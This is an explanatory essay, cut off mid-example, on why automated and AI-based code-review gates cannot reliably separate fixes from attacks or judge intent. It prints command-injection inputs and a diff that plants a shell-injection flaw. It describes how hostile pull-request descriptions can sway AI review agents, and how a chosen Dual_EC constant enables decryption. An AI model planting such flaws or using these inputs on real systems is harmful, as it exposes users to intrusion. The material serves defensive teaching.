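# Why automated security review cannot reliably tell a code fix from an attack, and what a code change shows about intent

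## Code changes, pull requests and automated security gates

Automated security review uses software to check a proposed change to a program for security problems before the change takes effect. Rule-based scanners have done this for years. Large language models, the AI systems behind chatbots such as ChatGPT, now do it too, and some can approve a change as well as comment on it. On GitHub, the largest site for hosting code, a project can let the site's AI reviewer, Copilot, supply an approval that the project's rules require (GitHub, *Copilot code review can now approve pull requests*, 2026).

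An automated security reviewer has to let repairs through and keep attacks out, but a repair and an attack can consist of the same few lines of code.

### How a change enters a project

Programmers keep a project's files in a repository, a store that also holds the project's history. Most of them manage it with a program called Git. A developer who has altered some files records the alteration as a commit and attaches a short message to it. Git can display the commit as a diff, a list of the lines that the change removes and adds:

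```diff
 function lookUp(hostname) {
-  return execFileSync("nslookup", [hostname]);
+  return execSync("nslookup " + hostname);
 }
```

In a diff, a minus sign marks a removed line and a plus sign marks an added one. Unmarked lines are unchanged and show where the edit falls in the file.

To get commits into the main version of the software, the developer opens a pull request, which GitHub's *Pull requests* defines as a proposal to merge code changes into a project. Merging means accepting the commits into the main version. The pull request's page shows the diff, the commits, automated test results, any scanner findings, and the author's description. Here, "description" means everything the author tells reviewers about the change: the title, the commit messages, the stated reason, and the tests the author claims to have run.

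The author of a pull request may be a stranger to the project's maintainers. On many open-source projects, anyone who can read the repository can copy it, change the copy without asking permission, and propose those changes to the project.

In the usual process described in *A Survey of Code Review Benchmarks and Evaluation Practices* (Khan, Wang and colleagues, 2026), the team then decides which changes to review first and gathers background on them, such as the affected files and related bug reports. A reviewer reads the change and comments, and the author revises it. This repeats until the reviewer accepts the change, often with automated tests along the way.

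A team can revert a merged change that turns out badly. In Git, a revert records new commits that reverse the effect of earlier ones, "often only a faulty one", in the manual's words. The same operation can remove a mistake or, if the earlier commit was a repair, bring the old fault back.

### One line in two directions

The diff above introduces a serious flaw. The code is written for Node.js, which runs JavaScript outside the browser. The function uses a program called nslookup to find the network address for a name.

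Node.js' *Child process* documents both calls. `execFileSync` takes the name of a program and a list of arguments, and by default starts the program directly. `execSync` takes a single string and passes it to a shell, the program that interprets typed commands. Some characters have special meanings in a shell. On Unix systems, for example, a semicolon separates one command from the next.

The two versions of the function behave alike for an ordinary name such as `example.org`. But if the name comes from a form on a public website, a visitor could type `example.org; ls`. The old version passes the whole string to nslookup as a name, and the lookup fails. The new version runs nslookup and then `ls`, which lists files on the server. The visitor could replace `ls` with almost any other command. The Node.js documentation for the shell-based call warns, "Never pass unsanitized user input to this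 function."

A flaw of this sort is a vulnerability: it lets someone break a security requirement of the software, a statement of what the software must never allow. This type has the number 78 in CWE, a public catalogue of types of software weakness that the American non-profit MITRE maintains. MITRE's *CWE-78* rates the likelihood of exploitation as high. Among its remedies, it advises programmers to find any function that invokes a shell with a single string and replace it with one that takes separate arguments. Applied to the flawed function, that advice produces this diff:

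```diff
 function lookUp(hostname) {
-  return execSync("nslookup " + hostname);
+  return execFileSync("nslookup", [hostname]);
 }
```

This is a fix, a change that removes a vulnerability. It contains the same code as the first diff, with the plus and minus signs swapped.

OSV's *GHSA-gxw4-4fc5-9gr5* (2025), an entry in a public vulnerability database, describes a real fix to a tool that connects AI assistants to the design program Figma. The tool built a shell command from unchecked input, so an attacker could add commands. The advisory recommends `execFile`, and version 0.6.3 of the tool adopted it and added input checks.

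Anyone who can read a project's history can find such a fix and propose its reverse. *SEVRA-BENCH* (Melo, Fogliato and colleagues, 2026) tests AI reviewers on changes that reverse old fixes. The two calls above come from one of its cases, where the description presented the change as routine "API normalization".

### Three things that people call an exploit

Strictly, an exploit is code or input that uses a vulnerability to cause the forbidden effect. The string `example.org; ls` is an exploit for the flawed version of `lookUp`. But people who talk of finding "an exploit in a diff" may mean any of three things, which call for different responses.

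A payload is code that itself carries out an attack. For example, an author might add a line to an installation script that reads the passwords saved on a developer's machine and sends them to an outside address. The harm begins as soon as somebody runs the script. The author can disguise the code, but the harmful instructions must be either in the change or in something it downloads.

Another is a planted vulnerability, a flaw that someone adds on purpose but that could pass for a mistake. The first diff is a planted vulnerability if its author knew about the semicolon. The diff contains no attack itself; that comes later, as input, perhaps from a different person, and until then the software works normally. A plainer sort of backdoor is hidden functionality that gives access to those who know its trigger, such as a secret password. Once a reviewer has found it, it is hard to pass off as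 a mistake.

The last is attack code that an honest developer includes to test a fix. A developer who repairs `lookUp` has good reason to add a test that calls it with `example.org; touch marker`. If the string reaches a shell, it creates a file named "marker" and the test fails. The string is a working exploit against the old version, but the pull request that contains it makes the software safer. Security advisories publish attack strings for similar reasons. For example, the Figma entry at OSV includes steps for confirming that an injected command runs.

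A check that searched only for attack strings would flag the honest test and pass the planted vulnerability.

### The kinds of gate and what each one reads

A gate is an automated check that can block a change (or, in front of an AI service, a user's request). In software projects, it runs after the author opens a pull request and before anyone merges it, usually alongside human review. Gates are appealing partly because they are fast. Cloudflare reports in *Orchestrating AI Code Review at scale* (2026) that the median wait for a first review on its internal projects was often hours.

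The oldest kind is pattern-based static analysis, which checks code against human-written rules without running it. *Secure by Design Alert*, issued by the American cybersecurity agency CISA and the FBI, recommends such rules against command injection. The two agencies were responding to attacks on network devices through three flaws listed in CVE, the public catalogue of known vulnerabilities. For Python software, they suggest that manufacturers forbid certain shell calls at the pull request stage. An equivalent rule for JavaScript would correctly flag the first diff above and pass its reverse. It would also wrongly flag an `execSync` call whose text is fixed in the program, so that no visitor can influence it. More elaborate analysers make fewer such errors by tracing data from where it enters the program to where the program uses it.

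Static analysis becomes a gate when its findings can stop a merge. Under GitHub's *Code scanning merge protection*, a project can block a pull request when a required tool raises an alert of a chosen severity, when the analysis is still running, or when nobody has configured the tool. An alert blocks the merge only if all the lines it identifies are in the diff. A change that sends a visitor's text to an existing shell call elsewhere in the project may therefore be merged if the alert points to that call.

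Trained classifiers learn from examples instead of applying written rules as static analysis does. Their developers collect code that people have labelled, for example as vulnerable or safe, and fit a statistical model to it. The model takes a piece of code, or measurements such as the size of a change, and returns a score. The gate blocks changes that score above a threshold set by the operator. Khan and colleagues surveyed 104 papers from 2015 to 2025 and found that machine-learning models and hand-written heuristics dominated research on automated review before large language models arrived.

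The newest kind of gate is the review agent, a language model that reads a pull request, may search the rest of the project, and approves or rejects the change. *Measuring and Exploiting Confirmation Bias in LLM-Assisted Security Code Review* (Mitropoulos, Alexopoulos and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes these autonomous agents from interactive assistants, which answer a human reviewer's questions and leave the decision to that person. Its example of an autonomous agent comes from xbmc, the project behind the Kodi media player. When somebody opens a pull request there, a hosted machine fetches the repository and starts Anthropic's Claude Code. The model's instructions are to be "extremely concise", to check for five things (bugs, security vulnerabilities, performance issues, logic errors and breaches of the style guide), and to approve if everything looks good.

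Review agents can read more than the other gates. In the tests by Melo and colleagues, an agent could inspect the state of the repository, the diff, the commit messages, and the title, description and comments of the pull request. This can help, because a flaw may depend on code outside the diff. But it also exposes the agent to the author's own account of the change, which a static analyser normally ignores and which a hostile author can write to persuade the agent.

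In practice these kinds overlap. GitHub (2025) announced that Copilot's reviews would combine a language model with the static analysers CodeQL and ESLint. Some AI reviewers give advice without acting as a gate. By default, Copilot leaves a comment, usually within 30 seconds, that does not count towards the approvals a project requires. Administrators can let Copilot give approvals that count, and can limit these to certain files. Any new commit cancels an approval already given. GitHub (2026) has also extended automatic reviews to pull requests that bots write. If a project requires one approval and lets Copilot's count, Copilot's can be the only one.

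### Detection rate and false-alarm rate

Two numbers describe how well a gate performs. The detection rate is the share of bad items that it flags, and the false-alarm rate is the share of harmless items that it flags. Suppose that a gate checks 1,000 changes, of which 10 introduce a vulnerability, with these invented results:

| | Flagged | Passed | Total |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Vulnerable changes | 8 | 2 | 10 |
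| Harmless changes | 99 | 891 | 990 |

The detection rate is 8 out of 10, or 80%. The false-alarm rate is 99 out of 990, or 10%. Mitropoulos and colleagues call these the true and false positive rates, and calculate them from files with a known vulnerability and repaired versions of such files.

Neither the detection rate nor the false alarm rate means much alone, because a gate could detect every vulnerable change by blocking all changes, or avoid false alarms by blocking none. The meaning of a flag also depends on the proportion of changes that are vulnerable. In the table, 99 of the 107 changes the gate flags are harmless, so a developer whose work it flags has usually done nothing wrong, even though the gate catches most of the vulnerable changes.

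### What a change does, whether it is dangerous, and why someone made it

The table leaves open what should count as a bad item. That depends on which of three questions the gate is supposed to answer.

Anyone who knows Node.js can see what the first diff does. The function used to start nslookup directly, and now it sends a string containing the hostname to a shell.

To judge whether the change is dangerous, the reader needs to know where the hostname comes from. If the program takes it from its own fixed list, no visitor can insert a semicolon and the change creates no vulnerability. If it comes from a public form, the server is open to attack. The reader also needs to know the security requirement, which in this case is that visitors must never choose which commands the server runs. Such requirements differ between programs, and developers often don't write them down anywhere in the code.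 For example, a public lookup page must prevent its users from choosing commands, but a tool built for administrators to run commands on a server has to allow it.

Replacing `execFile` with a shell-based call is dangerous, but the developer's intent may be honest. According to the Node.js documentation, `execFile` cannot launch Windows batch files and does not support shell features such as redirecting output to a file. A developer who needed either might switch to the shell-based call without considering that the shell could run commands inserted into its input. An attacker could write the same line and give the same reason for it.

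If a gate blocks an honest developer's dangerous mistake, that counts as a success when the aim is to catch vulnerable changes, but as a false alarm when the aim is to catch hostile ones. The distinction hardly matters when deciding whether to block the change, because the flaw would expose users equally whether or not it was deliberate. It matters much more when the project must decide whether to help the author fix the code or exclude them.

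## Theory: what the text of a change can and cannot establish

Someone who reads a diff may be unable to reach a verdict on it for four separate reasons. Every general method of analysis fails on some programs. Whether code is safe can depend on a security requirement that nobody wrote down. Honest and hostile authors can submit identical lines. Finally, cryptography lets an author choose a dangerous value that looks exactly like a safe one. The proofs about program analysis are the most famous of these results, but they matter least for ordinary pull requests.

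### Why no gate can judge every program correctly

In *Classes of Recursively Enumerable Sets and Their Decision Problems*, Rice (1953) proved that no general method can decide, for every program, whether its behaviour has a given property. The only exceptions are trivial properties, which belong to every program or to none. Rice worked with programs that list sets of numbers, but computer scientists apply the theorem to program behaviour in general. It covers whether a visitor can make a server run a command, which is a property of behaviour, but not whether a file contains the word `execSync`, which is a property of the text that a simple search can check.

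Fred Cohen, who did the first formal work on computer viruses, gave a short proof of a similar result. Cohen (1987), in *Computer Viruses*, defined a virus as a program that can infect others, meaning that it inserts a copy of itself, possibly an altered one, into their code. His argument runs as follows:

1. Suppose that somebody has written a perfect detector, D. Given the text of any program, D always finishes and correctly answers "virus" or "not a virus".
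2. Write a program, C, that runs D on C's own text.
3. Make C do the opposite of what D predicts. If D answers "virus", C infects nothing. If D answers "not a virus", C infects another program.
4. Whichever answer D gives about C is wrong, so a perfect detector cannot exist.

Evans, in *On the Impossibility of Virus Detection* (2017), reaches the same conclusion from Alan Turing's proof that no program can always tell whether another program will finish or run forever. His method carries over to code changes. Take any program P, and consider a pull request that runs P just before the unsafe version of the `lookUp` function:

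```diff
 function lookUp(hostname) {
-  return execFileSync("nslookup", [hostname]);
+  runP();
+  return execSync("nslookup " + hostname);
 }
```

If P finishes, the server reaches the shell call, and a visitor can insert commands. If P runs forever, the server never reaches that call. A gate that always judged such changes correctly could therefore tell whether any program finishes, which Turing proved impossible. The argument works only if P itself does no damage. Evans handles the equivalent problem for viruses by making P write to a temporary copy of the file system, which the computer then destroys.

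Neither proof depends on how the detector works, so both apply to language models as well as written rules. Cohen also proved that no method can always decide whether two versions of a program are equivalent. A gate therefore cannot verify every claim of "refactoring, no change in behaviour". Selcuk, Orhan and Batur's review of such results includes the detection of malicious behaviour that waits for a trigger.

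These worst-case results show that a gate which always gives an answer must be wrong about some program, but not how often it will be wrong about the pull requests people actually send. Cohen's program C has to contain the detector and run it on itself, which would be very unusual in a pull request. The original flaw in `lookUp` doesn't depend on any such construction, and anyone who knows Node.js and where the hostname comes from can find it by reading a few lines. Rice added, "Of course there will exist special methods for particular functions."

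A gate can also block whatever it cannot analyse, an option the perfect detector in the proofs lacks. The ban on certain shell calls that CISA and the FBI recommend works this way, though it causes some false alarms.

Cohen suggested accepting some false alarms and missed detections to catch many viruses. Spinellis (2002) studied the narrower task of recognising a known virus of limited length that rewrites itself as it spreads. He proved that perfect recognition is NP-complete, which means no known method stays fast as the problem grows. But he also described a detector for his example virus that, by accepting a few false alarms, runs in time proportional to the length of the input.

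Evans points out that real computers have finite memory, so in principle one could decide whether a program finishes by running it until it stops or repeats an earlier state. This is impractical because a machine with only 16 kilobytes of memory has 2^131,072 possible states. He more usefully suggests that a defender can run a suspicious program under restrictions, such as limits on which files it can change, without first deciding whether it is a virus.

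Worst cases deserve more attention in security than elsewhere because an attacker chooses which case the gate must handle. Cohen imagined a scanner that recognises one virus by the text `1234567` on its first line. It works until the attacker changes the line to `123456`. He concluded that a defender can build a detector for any particular virus, and an attacker can build a virus to evade any particular detector. Such evasion is a practical problem for gates, but it arises from known gaps in what they detect and would exist even if Rice's theorem were false.

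### Danger depends on a security requirement

Even a perfect virus detector would flag some programs that people want. Cohen's examples include a program that, with the user's permission, compresses other programs to save disk space and attaches itself to them so that it can unpack them later. It meets his definition of a virus. So does a compiler, the tool that translates source code into a runnable program, when a developer uses it to compile a new version of itself. Similarly, Evans notes that a program that replaces the advertisements in web pages could be malware or an ad blocker that the computer's owner installed on purpose.

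The same problem arises with small code changes. This one deletes a check from a login function:

```diff
 function logIn(account, password) {
-  if (account.failedAttempts >= 5) return false;
   return checkPassword(account, password);
 }
```

Assume that `checkPassword` counts the wrong passwords for each account. The deleted line refused all further logins after five failures.

On a public website where people choose their own passwords, an obvious security requirement is that strangers must not be able to guess their way into an account. A change that removes the check against guessing introduces a vulnerability, because an attacker can then have a program try millions of common passwords.

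Now suppose that the accounts belong to patient monitors in a hospital, and that each "password" is a random key stored in the device and too long to guess. The main requirement is that an outsider must never be able to cut off a monitor. With the check in place, anyone who can reach the server and knows a monitor's account name can lock that monitor out by sending five wrong keys, so deleting the check is a fix.

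A project might have both requirements, for instance if nurses log in with ordinary passwords and must never lose access. Both versions of the function would then be vulnerable, and the developers would need another design, such as a growing delay between attempts from the same address. The diff doesn't show which of these situations applies.

Software testers call a source of correct answers an oracle. *Just-in-Time Catching Test Generation at Meta* (Becker, Chen and colleagues, 2026) distinguishes an implicit oracle, which covers failures, such as crashes, that are wrong in any program, from the general oracle, the full set of expected behaviour. It describes the general oracle as "often ill-defined and only partly knowable". The paper's system writes tests that pass on the old version of the code and fail on the proposed one. Such a test shows that behaviour has changed, but not whether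 anybody wanted the change.

In 41 cases, the team at Meta therefore sent an engineer a short message describing the new behaviour and asking whether it was intended. The engineers confirmed a bug in 8 cases, 4 of which would have caused serious failures. Those who had wanted the new behaviour needed only a few minutes to dismiss the question. The study covered bugs in general, not security flaws in particular, but security review has the same difficulty telling whether new behaviour is intended.

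Reviewers who guess at a missing requirement can also guess too strictly. *Fabricated conditions in AI security reports* (2026), by the open-source maintainer defnull, describes AI-generated reports that ignore assumptions a program's developers are entitled to make. One report warned that an attacker who obtained the secret key a web application uses to sign the data it stores in cookies could run code on the server. That is true, but the application's security depends on keeping the key secret, and the report gave no way to steal it. Another report presented an error as a possible attack, but the error came from calling an internal function directly, which bypassed the safeguards that normally surround it.

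This limit applies to the text of the diff, and maintainers can overcome it by writing the project's requirements down where the gate can read them. Once the hospital has stated that no outsider may lock out a monitor, whether the code lets one do so is a technical question. Many requirements are also so common that a gate can safely assume them. For example, hardly any public website is meant to let visitors run commands on its server.

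### What an identical edit reveals about intent

Even if a gate has access to the requirement and correctly finds that a change is dangerous, the author may not have meant harm. Bayes' rule, the standard formula for updating a probability on new evidence, shows how far the diff can help determine intent.

The rule is simplest when stated in odds. If 1 author in 1,000 is hostile, the odds that a given author is hostile are 1 to 999. Reading the diff changes these odds as follows:

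odds after reading = odds before reading × likelihood ratio

The likelihood ratio is the probability that a hostile author would submit this diff, divided by the probability that an honest author would. A ratio above 1 raises the odds that the author is hostile, and a ratio below 1 lowers them.

Imagine 1,000 projects that each contain the safe version of `lookUp`. In each project, one developer submits the edit that replaces `execFileSync` with `execSync`. Of these developers, 999 are honest and want a feature of the shell. The last one knows about the semicolon and plans to use it. All the honest developers and the hostile one have submitted the same edit, so both probabilities are 1 and so is their ratio:

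1/999 × 1 = 1/999

Suppose 1,000 authors submit the same diff and one of them is hostile. The chance that any particular author is hostile is 0.1%, and reading the diff does not change it. A gate with fixed rules that reads only the diff must either accuse all the authors, 999 of them wrongly, or accuse none and miss the attacker. A language model may give different answers on different runs, but if its only input is the diff, it accuses authors at random.

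An edit is no evidence of its author's intent if honest and hostile authors are equally likely to write it. Even if only 1% of each group would write it, the likelihood ratio is still 1. This holds even when the diff is strong evidence of a vulnerability.

By contrast, almost no honest author would write an edit such as an installation script that steals saved passwords. Suppose 1 hostile author in 10 would submit such an edit, but only 1 honest author in a million would, perhaps as a security exercise sent to the wrong project. The table compares this edit with two versions of the shell example, again assuming that 1 author in 1,000 is hostile. All the figures are invented.

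| Edit | Hostile authors who would submit it | Honest authors who would submit it | Likelihood ratio | Chance that the author is hostile |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| Shell call, equally common in both groups | 1 in 100 | 1 in 100 | 1 | 0.1% |
| Shell call, more common among attackers | 20 in 100 | 1 in 100 | 20 | 2% |
| Code that steals passwords | 1 in 10 | 1 in 1,000,000 | 100,000 | 99% |

In the middle row, attackers are 20 times as likely as honest developers to make the edit, yet 98% of the people who make it are honest. In the last row, the diff alone is nearly enough to establish intent.

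So a diff can still reveal intent under the odds argument, and a payload often does. The argument applies to planted vulnerabilities, because an attacker can choose from the mistakes that honest developers often make. Cohen saw the same problem in monitoring computers for viruses. An event that is rare in normal use carries a lot of information when it occurs, but an attacker who knows the alarm threshold can keep the virus's activity below it.

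How close the ratio comes to 1 for a given kind of edit is an empirical question. Evidence from outside the diff has its own likelihood ratio, and the nearest such evidence is the author's description of the change. Becker and colleagues call working out the intention behind a code change "inherently problematic", and have a language model estimate it from the change's title and summary as well as the code. By intention they mean the behaviour the developer wanted, and the developers they study are coworkers with little reason to lie. A hostile stranger can write the same title and summary as an honest developer, which moves the description's ratio back towards 1.

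### A dangerous constant that looks random

A reader who knows the requirement and the source of the hostname can tell that the `lookUp` code is dangerous. Cryptography can hide a danger even from a reader who knows the code's requirements and the source of its inputs. The best-known example is Dual_EC, a method of generating random-looking numbers. The US National Security Agency (NSA) designed it, and the American standards agency NIST adopted it.

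Encryption needs numbers that outsiders cannot predict. A pseudorandom number generator produces them by stretching a short secret, its internal state, into a long stream. Dual_EC does this with points on an elliptic curve, a type of curve where two points can be added to get a third. Multiplying a point by a whole number means adding it to itself that many times. A computer can do this quickly, but nobody has published a practical way to undo it for curves of the size that Dual_EC uses. Given two points P and Q, an outsider cannot feasibly find the number d for which P = dQ.

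P and Q are public constants in the program. Starting from a secret state s₀, the generator works like this:

1. It multiplies P by s₀ and takes the horizontal coordinate of the result as its new state, s₁.
2. It multiplies Q by s₁ and outputs 30 of the 32 bytes of that point's horizontal coordinate.
3. It multiplies P by s₁ to get the next state, s₂, and continues in the same way.

In 2007 Dan Shumow and Niels Ferguson, two cryptographers at Microsoft, showed how somebody who knows d can break the generator. The eavesdropper sees the 30 bytes and soon finds the point s₁Q by trying all 65,536 possibilities for the missing two. Multiplying this point by d gives d × s₁Q = s₁ × dQ = s₁P, and the horizontal coordinate of s₁P is the next state, s₂. With s₂, the eavesdropper can calculate everything the generator will produce.

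A designer can easily create a Q with a known d by picking a secret number e, setting Q = eP, and calculating d from e. The resulting Q looks like any other point on the curve.

Somebody used this property against the network equipment maker Juniper Networks. Its ScreenOS software ran devices for virtual private networks (VPNs), which carry encrypted traffic over public lines. In 2008 Juniper added Dual_EC to ScreenOS with its own Q. The design was supposed to pass the output through a second generator, which would have blocked the known attack, but a bug in a loop counter kept that generator from running in the default configuration.

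In 2012 an intruder altered the ScreenOS source code. Juniper announced the discovery of "unauthorized code" in December 2015 and released a patch, but gave few details. Checkoway, Cohney and colleagues, in *A Systematic Analysis of the Juniper Dual EC Incident* (2016), report that the relevant difference between the vulnerable and patched versions was the value of Q, along with the expected results of a self-test. The intruder's edit had this form, with invented digits:

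```diff
-Q_x = 7c1f09d4...e2
+Q_x = b46a53f8...91
```

Juniper's first repair put the old constant back. Attack and repair each replaced one random-looking number with another, and updated the self-test to match.

Checkoway, Maskiewicz and colleagues (2018), in *Where Did I Leave My Keys?*, showed that such a swap is enough to let an attacker decrypt VPN traffic. They bought a Juniper device, generated a Q for which they knew d, and installed it with matching test values. They then recorded VPN connections to the device and decrypted each connection using only the traffic from that connection.

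No test of the software would have exposed the intruder's change, because the output with the new Q was cryptographically indistinguishable from the output with the old one. Checkoway and colleagues note that a maliciously generated Q normally has the same distribution as a random one. In that case, the likelihood ratio for its digits in Bayes' rule is exactly 1, so the digits are not evidence of how Q was generated.

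The researchers could not say whether the repaired version was safe either. Juniper had not explained how it generated its original Q, so someone might have known the corresponding d. The danger depends on whether anyone does, which cannot be determined from the code. The 2018 article suggests looking for answers in Juniper's version history, bug tracker and internal email, and in its engineers' memories.

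Where it applies, this limit is the most complete of the four, because neither reading the program nor running it reveals the danger. But it applies only to code whose security depends on a hidden mathematical relationship. A reviewer who can't tell what the edit means can still see that somebody has changed a cryptographic constant, which developers rarely have reason to do, and can ask where the new value came from. Published procedures exist for generating Q in a way that others can check, which makes it unlikely that anyone knows d. A gate could reject any new constant without such a derivation, and nobody would have to guess the author's motives.

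### Backdoors that pass for mistakes

Intent also affects whether people call a flaw a backdoor. Thomas and Francillon (2018), in *Backdoors*, define a backdoor as "an intentional construct" that undermines a system's expected security by giving access to privileged functions or information. It has four parts: a source of input, a trigger, a privileged state such as an administrator's session, and a route from the trigger to that state. Zdziarski (2016), in *Backdoor*, proposes a different test, which also requires intent and sets conditions on consent and access. Under either definition, someone who understands everything a flaw does may still not know whether it is a backdoor.

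Thomas and Francillon sort suspicious code into three classes by asking whether the route from the trigger to the privileged state is written explicitly in the program:

- In an intentional backdoor, it is. An example is a login function that compares the password with a fixed secret word and lets the user in if they match.
- In a deniable backdoor, the route depends on something that looks like a bug, but non-technical evidence suggests that somebody put it there on purpose.
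- In an accidental vulnerability, the route also depends on a bug, and nothing suggests any purpose.

A deniable backdoor is a planted vulnerability. Thomas and Francillon write that, from a purely technical perspective, it "will be indistinguishable from an accidental vulnerability". The unsafe `lookUp` could be either. An investigator can check the version history for who added the flaw and when, and can ask whether the change had a legitimate reason. Thomas and Francillon count such findings as evidence, but say the findings rely on human intuition and are not proof.

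They applied the scheme to eleven real backdoors, most of them in routers, cameras and video recorders. One D-Link router, for example, let in anyone whose browser identified itself with a particular string of letters and digits. All eleven had explicit routes, so none was deniable, and the authors argue that the people who put them there should be held accountable. The twelfth case was harder to classify. For academic research, two researchers had modified the web server Nginx so that a malformed request could trigger hidden instructions. The trigger looked like an ordinary mistake with uninitialised variables, but the hidden instructions would be difficult to explain innocently if anyone found them.

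The count of eleven to none does not show that deniable backdoors are rare, because it includes only cases that someone had already recognised as backdoors. A planted vulnerability that fooled everyone would appear in the records as an ordinary bug, with a CVE number and a routine fix. The cases do show that many real backdoors are crude enough to recognise from the code. The ScreenOS intrusions also included a crude backdoor, a hard-coded password that gave administrator access. Somebody had added it by 2013, and researchers identified it quickly after Juniper's announcement.

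### Does a gate need to know the intent?

One response is that a gate should ignore intent and assess only effects, since a planted flaw and an honest mistake expose users equally. A gate that blocks dangerous changes from everyone does not have to identify the one attacker among 1,000 developers or accuse anyone. It can report that a visitor could run commands through line 2 and suggest the safer call. This lets an honest author fix the line without giving a hostile author any benefit.

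This argument is largely right for deciding whether to merge a change. It is also a reason not to build a gate that tries to judge intent, since such a gate will have to rely on the author's description and may pass dangerous code because the explanation sounds sincere.

But this argument depends on the gate judging effects reliably, and no gate catches everything. Intent matters when the gate is imperfect, because an attacker can look for flaws it misses, while honest developers make mistakes without regard to what it can detect. Suppose a gate catches 80% of vulnerable changes. An honest mistake then has a 20% chance of getting through. An attacker with a private copy of the gate could test ten different vulnerable changes and submit one that passes. If the results were independent, the chance of finding at least one would be 1 − 0.8¹⁰, or about 89%. In practice, a gate that catches one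 version of a flaw is more likely to catch similar versions, so the attacker's chance would be lower than 89% but still higher than 20%. A detection rate measured on honest mistakes therefore overstates the protection against deliberately planted flaws.

The Dual_EC constant Q is a different kind of exception, because its effect depends on what its author knows. An intruder who generates Q and keeps the secret d can carry out the known attack, but that Q looks as random as a safe one from an honest engineer who kept no secret. A gate that judges changes by their effects cannot tell the two values apart, so it can only require proof of how the author generated Q.

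Intent matters most after review has accepted or rejected a change. If someone planted a flaw, the maintainers need to remove that person's access and re-examine everything else they contributed, as people had to do after a backdoor was found in the compression tool XZ in 2024. If the flaw has already reached users, intent also affects how urgent the response is. An accidental flaw may go unnoticed for years, but whoever planted a deliberate one has known about it from the start, so investigators should look for signs that someone has already used it.

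These decisions can usually wait until a person has gathered evidence from outside the diff, but a merge gate has to respond while the pull request is open. A gate can therefore block a change as dangerous without labelling it an attack. Code that steals passwords is an exception because the diff itself is strong evidence of intent, and a project would be justified in suspending the author's access at once while somebody investigates.

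## Incident reports: honest and hostile changes of the same form

Open-source projects keep their history in public, so when an edit turns out to have opened a security hole, anyone can look up the changed lines, the author's stated reason, and what other developers said about it. Readers can use these records to compare honest and hostile edits that look alike. Each edit in this table weakened a program's security or could have done so.

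| Year | Software | Edit | Stated reason | Author's purpose |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 2003 | Linux kernel | Two new lines that look like an error check | None | Hostile |
| 2006 | Debian's OpenSSL | Two lines disabled | To silence a testing tool's warnings | Honest |
| 2020 | OpenSSH | A guard around logging code removed | To rework the logging code | Honest, as far as anyone knows |
| 2021 | libarchive | One print function swapped for another | To add detail to an error message | Never established |
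| 2021 | PHP | New code that runs instructions from a web request | "Fix typo" | Hostile |
| 2024 | XZ Utils | New binary test files | To test the software | Hostile |
| 2024 | XZ Utils | A new feature check with a stray full stop | To make the check more accurate | Hostile, according to the maintainer |

### Debian's OpenSSL, 2006

OpenSSL is a library that programs use for encryption, and Debian is a widely used version of Linux that distributes its own copy. Debian's *Bug#363516* (2006) records that a user, Richard Kettlewell, reported a problem on 19 April 2006 under the title "valgrind-clean the RNG" (random number generator). Valgrind warns when a running program uses memory that it has not yet filled with data. Such warnings often point to a bug, and OpenSSL's generator was triggering them.

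The maintainer of Debian's package found the two lines responsible and asked OpenSSL's developers about removing them. *The perils of security tools*, a message to a cryptography mailing list, quotes his question. He thought that disabling both lines was the best option, but he added, "I have no idea what effect this really has on the RNG." As far as he could tell, the generator might just collect less entropy, meaning less unpredictable data. Debian went ahead and disabled both. Simplified, and with new comments to show where each line stood, the edit was:

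```diff
 /* where a program puts unpredictable data into the generator */
-MD_Update(&m,buf,j);

 /* where a program takes random numbers out */
-MD_Update(&m,buf,j);
```

`MD_Update` mixes the contents of a block of memory, `buf`, into the generator's calculations, and the same line appears in two places. Where a program takes numbers out, `buf` is the space waiting for the result, so the line mixes in whatever was already there. Deleting it there does no harm, and OpenSSL's developers, who knew that testing tools complained about it, had provided a setting that leaves it out. Where a program puts data in, `buf` holds the seed, the unpredictable data on which everything else depends, so deleting the line there ruins the generator.

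After the edit, almost the only thing that still varied between runs was the process ID, the number the operating system gives each running program. *Lessons from the Debian/OpenSSL Fiasco* reports that Debian's tool for creating SSH keys, which people use to log in to servers, could then produce only 32,767 different keys of a given type and size. An attacker could generate all of them in advance and try each one. The essay dates the change to September 2006, although Debian closed the bug report on 14 May that year. Either way, the flaw, now listed as CVE-2008-0166, went unnoticed for about two years.

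The evidence that the maintainer meant well is outside the diff. A user had complained about warnings that anyone with Valgrind could reproduce. The maintainer then showed the exact lines to the people best able to object and told them he did not understand the consequences. An attacker might do the same for cover, but one careful answer from an OpenSSL developer would have stopped the attack.

Even after Debian announced the flaw, some people misread the edit and concluded that OpenSSL's security had depended on leftover memory. Kettlewell (2008) told them in *Bug#363516* that it had not, and that they should take a few minutes to read the code.

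### OpenSSH, 2020

Most administrators use OpenSSH to log in to servers remotely. Its server program, sshd, gives each visitor a limited time to log in. When the time runs out, the operating system interrupts sshd and makes it run a short function called a signal handler. The interruption can come while sshd is halfway through rearranging its memory. If the handler then calls a function that also rearranges memory, such as the standard one for writing to the system log, an attacker who gets the timing right may be able to run code on the server.

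Mark Dowd reported a flaw of this kind in 2006, and the developers put a guard around the logging code. In October 2020 a commit with the title "revised log infrastructure for OpenSSH" removed the guard. Stripped of its surroundings, the edit was:

```diff
-#ifdef DO_LOG_SAFE_IN_SIGHAND
   /* write a message to the system log */
-#endif
   _exit(1);
```

The compiler includes the code between `#ifdef` and `#endif` only if somebody has defined the name on the first line, which here declares that logging is safe on that system. Without the guard, sshd always tried to write to the log. The old flaw returned in the default configuration and stayed until 2024, when researchers found it and it was assigned the identifier CVE-2024-6387.

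The repair has the same form as the mistake. Solar Designer (2024), in *openssh-9.8p1-upstream-cve-2024-6387.patch*, adapted it for another version of Linux:

```diff
+#if 0
   /* write a message to the system log */
+#endif
   _exit(1);
```

The compiler always skips code after `#if 0`, so sshd now exits without logging anything. Someone who did not know about signal handlers would see both changes as routine cleanup, and might prefer the harmful one because logs help administrators.

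The researchers who found the flaw called the removal accidental. The commit did rework the logging code, as its title said, and nobody has reported any sign of a hidden purpose. Under Thomas and Francillon's scheme, that is enough to class the flaw as an accidental vulnerability. But the evidence is weaker than in the Debian case, where the author had explained his thinking beforehand. An attacker who wanted to reintroduce the 2006 flaw could have made the same edit under the same title, and SEVRA-BENCH builds its hostile pull requests this way.

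### The Linux kernel, 2003

In 2003 the developers of the Linux kernel, the core of the operating system, kept the official source code in a system called BitKeeper. BitMover, the company that made BitKeeper, also published a copy for people who preferred an older system, CVS. On 5 November BitMover's Larry McVoy told the kernel developers that somebody had altered a file in the CVS copy. McVoy (2003), in *BK2CVS problem*, posted the added lines:

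```diff
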